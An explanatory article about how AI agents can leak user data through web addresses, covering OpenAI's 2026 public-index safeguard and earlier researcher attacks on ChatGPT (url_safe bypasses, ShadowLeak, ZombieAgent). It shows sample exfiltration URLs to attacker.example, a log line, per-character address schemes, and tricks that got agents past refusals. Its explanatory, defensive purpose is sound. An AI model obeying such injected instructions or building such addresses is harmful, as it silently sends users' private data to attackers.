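# OpenAI's January 2026 warning about malicious links and AI agents

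## What did OpenAI warn about, and how can a link leak data?

On 28 January 2026, Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell of OpenAI, the company that makes ChatGPT, published *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*. The post describes one way an AI agent can leak its user's private information. An AI agent is a language model that takes actions for a user, such as opening web pages, reading email or calling other software. An attacker who can influence what the agent reads may be able to trick it into requesting a web address that contains the user's data. The request itself delivers the data to whoever runs the site. The user doesn't have to click anything, and the chat may show no sign of the leak.

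Data exfiltration is the security term for sending private data to an outsider without authorisation. OpenAI calls it URL-based data exfiltration when the data leaks through a URL, or web address. OpenAI's post and the accompanying technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, both describe a safeguard in ChatGPT that lets the agent open an address automatically only if an independent crawler, a program that collects public web pages as a search engine does, has already found it. Six weeks later, in *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), OpenAI called this safeguard Safe Url.

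In *Understanding prompt injections*, published on 7 November 2025, OpenAI promised a report on how it detects when its AI's internet traffic would carry information out of a user's conversation. The January post fits that promise, and it reads more like an explanation of a safeguard than an alarm. It reports no new incident and names no victim.

### Agents, addresses and server logs

A chatbot that only writes text can reveal a secret only to the person reading the screen, but an agent can also contact other computers. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes the agent mode in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser. The agent views pages, clicks and types inside the user's own browser, with access to the same data as the user. ChatGPT's Deep Research feature carries out long research tasks, and users can connect it to a Gmail account. Even a plain question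 to ChatGPT may lead it to open a page or load a picture. At each of these steps, the agent requests something from another computer by sending a URL.

URLs have several parts, which MDN's *What is a URL?*, a page from a reference site for web developers, sets out in order. Take this invented example:

`https://shop.example/search/shoes?size=42&colour=red#reviews`

The opening `https` is the scheme, or method of transfer. The domain, `shop.example`, determines which server receives the request. The path, `/search/shoes`, once stood for a file's location on the server but is now mostly a label that the server can interpret in any way. The parameters, after the question mark, are pairs of names and values that give the server extra information. The anchor, after the `#`, marks a spot within the page. According to MDN, a browser never sends the anchor to the server. The path and parameters do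 go to the server, and the sender can put almost any text in them, including text the site has no use for.

Ordinary websites depend on this. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the harmless example of a user who asks where to find cars for sale nearby. ChatGPT knows that the user lives in London and offers a link whose path ends in "London". Including the city makes the link more useful, and following it tells the car site where the user lives. A rule against URL parameters would miss this because the city is in the path, not after a question mark.

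The site's owner can read the data that arrives because web servers keep records of requests. Apache's *Log Files*, part of the manual for a popular web server, describes an access log with a line for every request that the server processes. In a typical set-up, the line holds the IP address of the machine that made the request (its number on the internet), the time, the request itself with its path and parameters, a status code and the size of the reply. A common variant adds the page the visitor came from and the name reported by the visiting software. An attacker can therefore collect stolen data using a standard server with standard logging. The page at the requested address does not have to exist, since the server also logs requests that end in an error.

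Encryption does not prevent this, because `https` protects a request from eavesdroppers along the way, but the attacker runs the server that receives and decrypts it.

### Prompt injection

For a leak to happen, something must get the agent to build an address with private data in it. The usual method is prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in content that a model reads, to get the model to do something its user did not ask for. OpenAI likens it to phishing, the fraudulent emails that trick people into handing over passwords. The attacker does not need access to the user's chat and can leave the instructions where an agent is likely to find them, such as in a comment on a holiday listing, a review or an email.

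Language models have trouble telling legitimate instructions from those a stranger has planted in the text they process. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of software that helps recruiters score CVs. The software combines its own instruction ("score this CV") and the candidate's CV into a single text, the prompt. The model then predicts the next token, a word or part of a word, from all the text so far. Nothing in that process marks which text is a command and which is material to work on. If a candidate has hidden a line in the CV telling the model to approve the application, the model may follow it just as it would the recruiter's instruction.

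The title of David C's article refers to SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into a form that expects, say, a surname, and carelessly written software runs the command. Programmers can reliably prevent this by passing the surname to the database through a separate channel, so that the database never treats it as a command. Language models have no such channel. David C grants that attacks become harder when developers label outside text or train a model to give more weight to its developer's instructions, but he doubts that these measures will ever stop every attack. He recommends using ordinary software to set firm limits on what the system can do once someone has fooled the model. *The Framing Gap* (2026), a paper with experiments on agents that leak data, also attributes the failure to confusion between instructions and data, which an attacker can exploit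 without defeating the model's training in good behaviour.

OpenAI wrote in March 2026 that most of the attacks it knows of fail because its safety training makes the agent refuse, though it gave no figures. It also said the attacks have changed. Early ones could be blunt commands pasted into a Wikipedia article. A 2025 example, which outside researchers reported to the company, was an email that looked like a routine follow-up about a staff restructuring. It told the assistant that it was authorized to submit an employee's name and address to a compliance system. In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user made one particular request. OpenAI's account mentions no separate fix for that email, but presents Safe Url as the backstop when an attacker does convince the agent. Safe Url is the kind of limit that David C recommends, since its check on the address works the same way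 whether or not the model has been deceived.

### One leak, step by step

Suppose Ruth is moving house and has connected an agent to her email. She asks it to look up her moving date and compare three removal firms. The agent searches her inbox and finds a message in which her solicitor says she leaves 22 Elm Road on 14 March and the buyers arrive two weeks later. Those facts are now part of the text the model works from.

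The agent then opens the firms' websites. One site lets anyone post a review, and an attacker has posted one that is mostly ordinary praise. The review also includes a passage formatted so that human visitors won't notice it. In this passage, the attacker claims that the site has a technical requirement: to get the firm's current prices, an assistant must load a picture from another server and include the customer's address and moving date in the request.

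If the model treats this as part of its task, it writes out an address of the same form as the one in OpenAI's own illustration:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=22-Elm-Road-empty-from-14-March`

The software around the model requests that address. The attacker's server sends back a blank picture and adds a line to its log:

`203.0.113.7 - - [03/Feb/2026:10:42:17 +0000] "GET /collect?data=22-Elm-Road-empty-from-14-March HTTP/1.1" 200 43`

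The attacker opens the log that evening and learns from the middle of the line which house will be empty, and from what day. The code 200 means that the request succeeded, and 43 is the size of the blank picture in bytes. Ruth sees only a comparison of three removal firms, and the prices may all be correct.

A filter that checks only what the agent writes to its user would miss the leak, because nothing in the visible answer is sensitive. Virus scanners would not help either, because no malicious program reaches Ruth's computer. The agent has used its normal ability to load pictures from the web.

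*The Framing Gap* lists three ingredients of such a leak: a confidential value in the text the model is working from, the ability to read untrusted outside content, and the ability to act on the outside world through tools. Ruth's agent had her email, the review page and the power to request web addresses. Removing any one of these would prevent this particular leak. Without access to her inbox, for example, the agent would have had no moving date to give away. This is why OpenAI advises users to let an agent see only the data it needs for the task. But the agent has to read outside pages to compare removal firms. Safe Url works on the third ingredient, the request. In terms OpenAI borrows from security engineering, the hostile review is a "source", a way to influence the system, and the power to send a request is a "sink", a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context.

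### Whose computer sends the request

The log line begins with an IP address, and depending on the product it may belong to Ruth's computer or to one of OpenAI's.

When data leaks through an image in the chat window, the user's own browser sends the request. Chat products often let the model format its replies in Markdown, a simple notation in which a short line of text stands for an image. The product turns that line into web code, and the browser fetches the image from whatever address the line contains. *Bing Chat*, an article on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, describes this behaviour in Microsoft's chatbot. The browser connected to the address without the user doing anything, and the address could contain private text. Microsoft closed that route in May 2023 by restricting the loading of images. Simon Willison's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web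 version* (2023) drew attention to the same weakness in ChatGPT, which Roman Samoilenko had found. Samoilenko's image was a single pixel, too small for a user to notice. OpenAI began to address the problem only in December 2023.

When the agent browses from OpenAI's servers, those servers send the request. OpenAI tells website owners in its documentation that ChatGPT may visit a page to answer a user's question, that it identifies itself as ChatGPT-User, and that OpenAI publishes the IP addresses it uses for these visits. A site's log would then show that name and OpenAI's address, and nothing about the user's own machine. The log would still contain the user's data, in the URL's path or parameters.

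An attack called ShadowLeak used this route. Paganini (2025) reported in *ShadowLeak* that researchers at the security company Radware found that a crafted email could make Deep Research, when connected to a user's Gmail, send inbox data to an attacker directly from OpenAI's cloud. The attack was zero-click, meaning the victim didn't have to do anything beyond using the product normally. OpenAI fixed the flaw after Radware reported it, according to SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Targeted in Server-Side Data Theft Attack*.

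Where the request comes from determines who can stop it. If the user's browser makes the request, the product can restrict which images the browser loads, and an employer's network filter might notice traffic to a strange site. Neither measure works on a request sent from OpenAI's data centre, because it never crosses the user's equipment, so only the company that runs the agent can stop it.

Sometimes the user sends the data by clicking a link that ChatGPT has written into its answer, as in the example of the London car buyer. Unlike a zero-click attack, this requires the user to act, but few people read a long address before clicking it. OpenAI therefore shows a warning before opening a link that it cannot verify as public. The user sees the address, with a notice that it may contain information from the conversation, and can check it for anything that should not be there.

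### Three meanings of "malicious link"

People who write about AI agents use "malicious link" for at least three different things, and OpenAI's safeguard deals with only one of them.

A malicious link may mean an address that carries data out, as in Ruth's case. Such a link is harmful because of what it contains and where it sends it, and the page behind it can be blank. A list of known bad pages would not necessarily include the address, because the agent composes it on the spot from one user's data. This is URL-based exfiltration, and OpenAI's one promise is to prevent the agent from quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself when it fetches something. The promise is limited to quiet leaks, since a user who reads the warning and opens the link anyway can still send the data.

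Others use the phrase for a link to a page that holds hostile instructions. The review that Ruth's agent read was on such a page. Its address contained nothing private, so a check that looks for private data in addresses would not flag it. The page was also open to everyone, and a search engine could have listed it for years. OpenAI states that the safeguard does not guarantee that a page's content is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* likewise says that the new measure addresses the channel through which data leaves, not prompt injection.

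A check on web addresses still leaves many harms from prompt injection possible. In one of OpenAI's examples, hidden text in a flat listing leads an agent to recommend that flat over better ones. The user gets bad advice, but no data leaves. In another, an agent with access to a mailbox finds the user's bank statements and shares them with an attacker who had sent it a misleading email. That is data exfiltration, but if the agent sends the statements by email, there is no web address to check.

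Finally, the phrase can mean a link that feeds a prompt to an assistant when a person clicks it. Some AI products accept a question in their own web address, through a parameter called `q`, so a link can open the assistant with the question already filled in. Researchers at the security company Varonis used this feature in an attack on Microsoft's Copilot that they named Reprompt. SecurityWeek reported that one click on a prepared link put the attacker's text into the assistant, and a chain of further requests then extracted the user's data, even after the user had closed Copilot. The link points to the assistant's genuine site and carries the attacker's words into the assistant. Varonis told Microsoft about the flaw on 31 August 2025, and Microsoft patched it on 13 January 2026, according to BeyondMachines, a security news site. The patch came two weeks before OpenAI's post, so readers that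 month could easily have confused the two problems.

A single attack can involve more than one of these links. Ruth's agent visited a page with hostile instructions, then built an address that carried her data out. OpenAI's safeguard would have let the agent read the page but would have intervened at the second address, because no independent crawler could have found it before the agent wrote it.

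### What the press made of it

Some of the coverage made the post sound broader and more alarming than it was. PYMNTS, a news site for the payments industry, ran one of the most prominent reports, *OpenAI Warns Malicious Links Could Undermine Agentic AI*. It claimed that OpenAI saw malicious links becoming "one of the most exploitable surfaces" as agents start to act, and that OpenAI placed links "on par with prompts and permissions" as a security risk. Neither statement appears in the post, which doesn't rank risks. Spânu and Shadwell introduced their subject as "one specific class of attacks". PYMNTS also dated the guidance to "Wednesday (Jan. 29)", but the post is dated 28 January, which was the Wednesday of that week.

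The ranking may be a defensible opinion, but OpenAI did not express it there. PYMNTS made a less visible error that matters more for understanding the safeguard. It wrote that OpenAI trains its agents to distinguish links that already exist on the public web from links that someone introduces during a conversation. OpenAI described a lookup. Before the agent fetches an address automatically, the system compares it with an index of addresses that a crawler has already recorded. A clever enough injection may overcome a model's training, but the result of a lookup doesn't depend on how persuasive the hostile page is. The PYMNTS report also did not separate links that carry data out from pages that contain hidden instructions, so a reader could think that the new check protects against both.

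Alex Rolfe's *Why malicious links are emerging as a systemic risk for agentic AI* repeats the comparison with prompts and permissions, then adds that OpenAI warns of malicious actors "increasingly exploiting" the way agents follow links. OpenAI's post contains no such warning and no count of attacks. Its closest statement is a forecast that adversaries will keep adapting as agents become more capable. AINews stayed closer to the original and explained that the check tests only whether an exact address is already public.

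In November 2025, less than three months before the warning, OpenAI had discussed real attackers in a calmer tone than the headlines. It wrote that it had "not yet seen significant adoption" of prompt injection by attackers, though it expected them to put considerable time and money into it.

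## Why did ChatGPT's earlier link protections fail?

The public-index check followed about two years of narrower rules, all of which researchers got around. A rule would stop the attack that prompted it but leave another way to get private data out through a web address. The attacks described here are researchers' demonstrations.

### The image leak of 2023

Roman Samoilenko found the leak at the end of March 2023, and Johann Rehberger did so independently a few days later, according to Rehberger's 2023 post *ChatGPT Plugins*. The leak worked because ChatGPT's web app displayed any image in the model's answer, even one whose address contained text from the chat.

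Samoilenko got instructions into a stranger's chat through the clipboard. When a visitor copied text from a prepared website, a script on the page added instructions to it. The visitor then pasted it all into ChatGPT. The model ended its answer with a transparent one-pixel image, whose address might contain the program code it had just corrected for the user. The instructions could also ask for an image in every later answer, so that each new question went to the attacker as well. SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* reported that the attack also worked when a user asked ChatGPT to summarise a prepared web page.

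Samoilenko warned that the early version of the attack was unreliable, since the model's answers vary and the same instructions might work on one try and fail on the next. Extracting the user's earlier questions or code was fairly easy, but extracting passwords and access keys was very difficult. Samoilenko thought OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from replying with images in this format at all.

Rehberger reported the problem to OpenAI in early April 2023. The company had no bug bounty programme yet, as Embrace The Red recalled in 2026, so they discussed it by email, without result for months. Embrace The Red's *HackSpaceCon New Important Instructions*, a set of slides by Rehberger, lists ChatGPT as "won't fix" in both September and November 2023. By November every other product on the list, including Bing Chat and Anthropic's Claude, had a fix.

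### url_safe and its gaps

OpenAI introduced a check called url_safe in December 2023. Before ChatGPT's web app displayed an image from an outside address, it sent the address to OpenAI's server, which marked it safe or unsafe. If the address was marked unsafe, the app did not load the image and the attacker's server received nothing. OpenAI did not publish the criteria, so outsiders could learn them only by trying addresses.

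Rehberger began testing ChatGPT's url_safe check the day it appeared, and Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the results. The check correctly rejected a URL with someone's email address attached. Rehberger then set up 36 image URLs on his own server, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them passed. He could not identify why the image for "a" appeared but the image for "d" did not. He sent the word "hi" to the server by having ChatGPT display approved images one after another.

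With only nine of the 36 characters usable, an attacker could in principle still represent every letter and digit, because nine addresses taken in pairs give 81 combinations. In practice, the model would have to encode the text correctly, and a browser may reuse an image it has already loaded instead of requesting it again. Rehberger considered the leak slow and easier to notice than the original attack, and suggested that OpenAI limit the number of images in each answer.

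ChatGPT's web app itself had to request the verdict, so every other ChatGPT app needed its own code to do the same. The iPhone app that Rehberger examined had no such check, and he thought the Android app probably lacked it too. Partly for this reason, Willison's December 2023 note on the change called it "half-baked". OpenAI added url_safe to its iPhone and Mac apps only in September 2024, according to Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*. For about nine months, an attacker could therefore avoid the new protection if the victim used the iPhone app.

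### Addresses already in the conversation

The security company Imperva later worked out part of the hidden rule. Its *From ChatBot To SpyBot* found that ChatGPT would display an image, or open a page with its browsing tool, only if the address had already appeared in the conversation. The reasoning was that the model could not have added anything to an address written before it began its answer.

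For images, url_safe did little more than search for text. It approved any string that appeared in what the user had supplied, including custom instructions (the preferences a user sets for all chats), even if the string wasn't a valid address. The check was less strict for a few well-known domains. For example, it accepted openai.com addresses with any path or parameters.

An attacker who could plant text in the conversation could also plant addresses there. Imperva listed one fixed address per character and had ChatGPT display the images that spelled out a secret. Another version used one long address ending in the digits and the alphabet. Every shortened form of that address also occurred in the conversation, so the model could send a character by cutting the address off there. An attacker could also buy a separate domain for each character, at a dollar or two each, because url_safe accepted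 any domain name with nothing after it.

The browsing tool had the same weakness. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, found that ChatGPT would open an address given in the prompt but would not insert the user's age into one. The attack therefore supplied a complete address for each age range and asked ChatGPT to open the one that applied. None of these addresses contained personal data, but the attacker could tell the user's age range by seeing which one appeared in the log. ChatGPT could choose the address without a stated age if the user mentioned having graduated from high school that day.

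Schwartzman could also extract longer values, such as a seven-digit postal code. The planted text contained a separate address for each position, and ChatGPT shortened each address to a length that stood for the digit. ChatGPT made mistakes doing this, so Schwartzman included a short program to work out the right addresses. At the time, ChatGPT opened no more than ten addresses per prompt and would not open the same one twice, so the attack could send only ten characters at a time. This was slow enough that a user might notice and stop it.

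Schwartzman reported the attack through Bugcrowd, the company that handles vulnerability reports for OpenAI, and was told it was not applicable. The paper came out in June 2024. Fifteen months later, Radware reported an attack that used the same principle, and this time OpenAI fixed it.

### Bing and the trouble with trusted names

ChatGPT's other test depended on the name of the site. In October 2024 Rehberger reported that url_safe approved addresses under windows.net, a domain that Microsoft uses for its cloud storage customers. Anyone can open a storage account there, get an address under Microsoft's domain and read the log of requests to it. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows how Rehberger used such an account to collect a user's recent chat history. The data went directly into the address instead of being spelled out letter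 by letter. OpenAI had not told Rehberger of a fix when the post appeared in 2025.

Such an attack requires a site that passes the check, accepts data in an ordinary request and lets the attacker see that data. An attacker could not see data sent to GitHub, the code-sharing site, because only its owner, Microsoft, could read the server logs. In an earlier demonstration, Rehberger therefore used GitHub pages to deliver instructions to ChatGPT and the storage account to receive the data.

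Tenable, another security company, found a different problem with trusted names and reported it to OpenAI on 10 December 2024. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* says that url_safe always approved addresses at bing.com, Microsoft's search engine. Each Bing search result links to a bing.com address that records the click and then redirects the visitor to the listed page. Any site that Bing indexes therefore also gets a bing.com address that leads to it.

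A redirect is a reply from a server that tells the browser to go to another address. Suppose a search engine has listed an attacker's page and given it this invented link:

`https://search.example/go/7f3a`

The browser requests the link, and the search engine's server replies that the page is at another address:

`https://attacker.example/h`

The browser then requests the second address without asking the user. A check that covers only the first address approves it because it belongs to a familiar search engine, but the request for `/h` still reaches the attacker's log. If that page stands for the letter h, the attacker has received one letter.

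The attacker cannot add text to a Bing link because the link is fixed when Bing creates it, so Tenable had Bing index a page for every letter of the alphabet. ChatGPT sent the word "hello" by displaying the links for h, e, l, l and o in order.

Tenable's *HackedGPT*, published in November 2025, combined this trick with several others. In one demonstration, an attacker left instructions in a comment on a blog post, and the user asked ChatGPT to summarize the post. A separate model, which Tenable calls SearchGPT, read the page but had no access to the user's memories or earlier messages. The comment made SearchGPT end its summary with instructions for ChatGPT, and the summary became part of the chat. A display fault hid those instructions from the user. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT followed the instructions and sent private data out through images with Bing addresses.

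Isolating SearchGPT had only delayed the attack, which left url_safe as the last barrier. url_safe failed because a site's name identifies only the server that receives the first request. The name doesn't show where a redirect will lead, or whether the site's owner rents out space to strangers who can read their own logs. OpenAI later cited redirects as a reason not to rely on lists of trusted sites, and added that a very strict list would produce so many false alarms that people would learn to click through the warnings.

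No source gives a firm date for the fix to the Bing bypass. Tenable asked OpenAI for updates until March 2025, and its advisory records no solution. On 11 July 2025, OpenAI told Tenable that it had improved "safe_url", presumably the same check, in response to a separate report about links that fill in and submit a prompt (Tenable, *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface*, 2025). Rehberger dates a further tightening to around August 2025. But two of Tenable's published demonstrations on GPT-5, a model released that August, use the bypass, so the July change did not block it completely.

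### ShadowLeak

url_safe checked what appeared in the chat window, but Deep Research ran on OpenAI's servers and opened pages from there. Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses Deep Research could open, and reported the vulnerability, ShadowLeak, on 18 June 2025.

In the demonstration, the victim's inbox contained a genuine personnel email with an employee's name and home address, as well as the attacker's email about a staff restructuring. When the victim asked Deep Research to go through the day's emails about a new employee, the agent read both. It then opened what the attacker's email presented as an employee lookup service, with the employee's details in the URL.

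According to Radware, the model's training offered some resistance. The agent refused to send the data when asked plainly and when the email claimed that the user had asked for it. It once treated the attacker's address as suspicious and searched for information about it instead of opening it. The researchers made progress when they named the browsing tool the agent should use and told it to try again after a failure. Retrying helped because the restrictions did not always give the same result.

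Even then, the agent sometimes opened the address without the personal details. The researchers solved this by having it first convert the details into Base64, which rewrites data as letters, digits and a few symbols. The email presented this as a security measure, although anyone can decode Base64. Radware believes the software carrying out the request then received only a harmless-looking string. This version worked every time in repeated tests. According to Radware's advisory, a simpler version worked about half the time, and adding urgency and a more plausible address improved that rate considerably.

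Accounts of the fix give two dates, which refer to different events. According to Radware's timeline, OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August 2025 without telling the researchers. OpenAI acknowledged the flaw and marked it as resolved on 3 September. A company press release, Radware (2025), mentions only September, as the date when OpenAI notified Radware. The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent* gives both dates, but its wording suggests that OpenAI announced the fix in August. Radware's timeline is more specific, and it indicates that the flaw stayed open for about seven weeks after it was reported.

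OpenAI then barred ChatGPT from altering URLs. ChatGPT could open a URL exactly as given, but would not add parameters even when told to. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* describes this as the response to attacks such as ShadowLeak. The rule would have kept the employee's details out of the URL, but it was very similar to the one Schwartzman had already bypassed in 2024.

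### ZombieAgent

Radware's Zvika Babo reported the next attack on 26 September 2025, just over three weeks after OpenAI marked ShadowLeak as resolved. Radware's *ZombieAgent* explains that the attacker's email contained a complete address for each letter, each digit and a space. ChatGPT found the private information, converted it to lower case and opened the matching address for each character in turn. This didn't break the rule against altering addresses, because ChatGPT opened each one exactly as supplied.

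Suppose the secret is "elm22", short for a street address. If each character had its own web address, ChatGPT would open the ones for e, l, m, 2 and 2. But the requests might arrive out of order, and ChatGPT might not open the address for 2 a second time because it stores pages it has already visited. The attacker could receive "m2el" and be unable to reconstruct the original.

Radware's solution was to supply a separate address for each character in each position. Counting positions from zero, and using an invented site, ChatGPT would open these five:

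`https://attacker.example/e0`  
`https://attacker.example/l1`  
`https://attacker.example/m2`  
`https://attacker.example/23`  
`https://attacker.example/24`

In the last two addresses, the first digit is the character and the second is its position. The repeated 2 now has two different addresses, so ChatGPT has no stored copy to reuse. The attacker can sort the requests by their final digits, whatever order they arrive in.

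Covering every letter and digit at each position in a ten-character block takes 360 addresses, 260 for the letters and 100 for the digits. Including the space would add another ten. A script can produce such a list in moments. For a given secret, ChatGPT opens only a few of these addresses. Its selection reveals the data, so a rule against changing the addresses cannot prevent the leak.

Three days after the first report, Babo sent an improved version that had worked in every test, and Bugcrowd reproduced the attack the next day. The user only had to ask ChatGPT to do something involving Gmail. Radware also hid instructions in files that a user might share with ChatGPT. It got data out through images in the user's browser too, though less reliably than through OpenAI's servers.

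### Memory and spread by email

ZombieAgent could continue after the first theft by using ChatGPT's memory, the feature that stores facts about a user between chats. OpenAI had tried to prevent this by blocking ChatGPT from using memory in any chat where it had already used a connected service such as Gmail. ChatGPT also would not open an attacker's addresses if they were stored in memory.

Babo found that ChatGPT could do the reverse, reading its memory first and then connecting to Gmail. In the attack, the victim shared a file once, and instructions in it added two rules to ChatGPT's memory. Under the first, ChatGPT would look up a particular email from the attacker whenever the user sent a message, and follow its instructions. Under the second, it would save any sensitive information the user mentioned. The list of addresses stayed in the email, so memory contained no address for OpenAI's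 restriction to block.

From then on, ChatGPT carried out the attacker's task before it answered each message, even in a new chat. SecurityWeek's *‘ZombieAgent’ Attack Let Researchers Take Over ChatGPT* described the result as a persistent spy tool. An attacker could also do harm without stealing anything, by changing the stored memories. Radware altered a user's saved medical history, and ChatGPT then gave misleading medical advice.

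To spread the attack, the email included instructions for ChatGPT to collect addresses from recent messages in the inbox and send them by the same character-by-character method, with a special character marking the end of each address. The attacker's server then sent the malicious email to those addresses, so denying ChatGPT permission to send email would not have stopped the spread. But new recipients would lose data only after connecting ChatGPT to their mailbox and asking it to do something there, which would limit how far the attack could spread.

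### The fix in December 2025

OpenAI fixed ZombieAgent on 16 December 2025, almost twelve weeks after the first report, and Radware published its findings on 8 January 2026. TechRadar's *This 'ZombieAgent' zero click vulnerability allows for silent account takeover* noted that Radware did not explain how the fix worked.

As Rehberger understands the public-index check that OpenAI described on 28 January, once a user enters an address in a message, ChatGPT also accepts it for the rest of that chat. Appearing elsewhere in the conversation is no longer enough. Radware's 360 addresses would fail if they arrived in an email and no crawler had seen them, because the user did not supply them. Samoilenko and Schwartzman got their instructions into the chat through pasted text, and Rehberger's description does not distinguish between addresses that a user types and those that arrive that way.

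## How does the check against a public web index work?

ZombieAgent worked because ChatGPT would open any address exactly as an email supplied it. Under the public-index check, before the agent opens an address on its own, ChatGPT's software checks whether that address is in a list that a crawler built from public web pages, without access to anyone's chats.

OpenAI set out the rule in its January post. Johann Rehberger's article on Embrace The Red adds details from the technical paper and from his own experience with ChatGPT.

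The design accounts for an attacker who has already fooled the model but doesn't know the user's private data, and so needs the agent to put that data into a request.

### The rule in steps

Before any chat begins, the crawler goes through public pages as a search engine does and records the addresses it finds. OpenAI calls the resulting index "independent", meaning independent of users, not of OpenAI. Rehberger had guessed in 2023 that ChatGPT might consult Microsoft's Bing index, but after reading the paper he reported that OpenAI checks URLs against its own index.

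When the agent needs something from the web, the check runs like this:

1. The agent chooses an address to open, or an image to show.
2. The software looks for the whole address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the agent can load it without asking the user.
4. If it is not, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning before anything opens.

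The January post describes a lookup that treats any unknown address as a possible leak. In March, OpenAI described Safe Url as a way to detect when information from a conversation would reach a third party. The lookup does not search the address for that information, such as names or account numbers, so an attacker gains nothing by disguising it. Encoding it in Base64, as in ShadowLeak, would still produce an address that no crawler has seen.

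The lookup has to cover the whole address, because an attacker could put stolen data in any part it ignored. The older url_safe check had this fault because it accepted openai.com addresses with any path or parameters. OpenAI's post refers to "this exact URL" but doesn't explain which small differences in spelling count as a different URL.

Those differences matter because two different addresses can lead to the same page. In *Fetch, Read, Reuse*, Chen, Canini and colleagues (2026) tested how OpenAI's page-fetching software handles such variants when it could reuse a page it had already downloaded. The software downloaded the page again if the researchers added a parameter, added a trailing slash or capitalised the path. It reused its copy if they only reordered the parameters or added an anchor. These tests concerned stored copies, and the safety check may follow different rules.

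### What the user sees

The user sees a warning titled "Check this link is safe", with a note that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The box shows the address, and the user can copy the link or open it. If something looks wrong, OpenAI advises avoiding the link and asking ChatGPT for another source or a summary.

This works best when the user can read the data in the address. Ruth, whose agent was comparing removal firms, would probably notice `22-Elm-Road` in a link to a site she had never heard of. In Base64, "22 Elm Road" becomes `MjIgRWxtIFJvYWQ=`, which looks like the codes in many harmless links. She wouldn't be able to see what was wrong, so her only reason to refuse the link would be that ChatGPT couldn't verify it.

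According to OpenAI's help page, the company scans websites for its search results and uses what it learns to decide when a link needs approval. If a site's owner asks OpenAI not to catalogue it, ChatGPT prompts the user to confirm every link to that site, no matter how old or public the page is.

Such a site may still get visits from ChatGPT. Website owners usually use a file called robots.txt to tell crawlers which pages they may read. Chen and colleagues never saw OpenAI's fetching software request that file. According to OpenAI's documentation, robots.txt may not apply to these visits because a person starts them. A newspaper can therefore keep its articles out of OpenAI's index and still have ChatGPT open one at a reader's request.

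### Why the crawler must know nothing about users

A match is a sign of safety only because of how OpenAI built the list. Suppose the crawler recorded `https://removals.example/prices` last month. The crawler had no access to Ruth's email, so that address can't contain a moving date taken from her inbox. When her agent opens the page, the firm learns that somebody wants its prices.

An address that the agent builds from her email would be on the list only if that exact address was already on the public web. The attacker could try to put it there in advance, but would have to guess the secret.

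Take a seven-digit code, which has ten million possible values, all equally likely. If an attacker publishes addresses for *k* of them and the crawler records every one, the chance that the list includes the right address is

*k* / 10,000,000.

With a thousand addresses, the chance is one in 10,000. The calculation applies only to a secret sent whole. An attacker who sends it one character at a time needs far fewer public addresses. Rehberger says OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its paper.

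OpenAI claims only that an address already public, independently of any user's conversation, is "much less likely" to contain that user's private data.

If OpenAI instead added every address that appeared in its users' chats, the hostile review could get Ruth's agent to write the attacker's address, with her moving date in it, in an answer. The system would add this address to its list, and the agent could then open it as a known address. The match would not show that the address was already public, because the conversation itself had produced the entry.

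User traffic would also bring private addresses into the index without any attacker planning it. Many websites send people links that contain a password-reset code or open a confidential document, and anyone who has such a link can use it. In *The Silent Spill*, Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues (2026) found that services that publish addresses from their users already have this problem. The researchers collected 6.09 million addresses from five public sources, including URLScan.io and VirusTotal, which scan submitted links for security threats and often make the results public. Email providers and company security systems also forward suspicious links to such services automatically, so a private link can become public without its owner doing anything.

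The researchers' software flagged 12,331 possible leaks, including 26 password-reset links, 83 access keys for software services and 12 open sessions for signing documents. When the researchers checked samples by hand, no more than 15 percent of any category were false alarms.

URLScan.io supplied 90 percent of the collection and 63.5 percent of the flagged addresses. About 0.14 percent of its addresses were flagged, compared with 0.5 percent for the Wayback Machine, an archive of web pages. Ramadan and colleagues searched by domain and keyword, so neither rate describes the web as a whole.

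The archive's result suggests that a crawler with no access to users could still record secrets that somebody else has exposed. This would give an attacker little help against OpenAI's check, because a password-reset link in the index was public before any agent opened it, and opening it sends the code back to the site that issued it.

OpenAI does keep a store of pages downloaded in response to user requests. In all three of their trials with the ChatGPT app, Chen and colleagues found that a page downloaded for one account was also used to answer a question from another. If the safety check treated these stored pages as public, a link that one user had approved could open automatically for everyone else. OpenAI says the index has no access to user data, which would rule this out, but Chen and colleagues did not test the check itself.

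### Why not a list of trusted sites?

A simpler rule would let the agent open only links to well-known websites. OpenAI accepts that this helps but gives two reasons for preferring a different approach.

One is redirects, the weakness behind Tenable's Bing bypass. Some reputable sites will forward a visitor to whatever destination the address names, as in this invented example:

`https://trusted.example/out?to=attacker.example/22-Elm-Road`

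A check on the site's name would approve this, and the redirect would then carry Ruth's street to the attacker's server.

Requiring an exact match blocks the first request in this example, because no crawler has recorded the trusted site's address with Ruth's street attached. It also limits later redirects. A server has only the information sent in the request, so if the first address contains nothing private, the server can't add Ruth's street to the second one. The attacker could still learn something from which public address the agent chose.

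OpenAI's post doesn't explain whether the software repeats the lookup after each redirect. When Chen and colleagues sent OpenAI's fetching software into an endless series of redirects, it followed one and stopped. The test used OpenAI's API, not the ChatGPT app, and it shows that the software limits how many redirects it follows, but not whether it checks where they lead.

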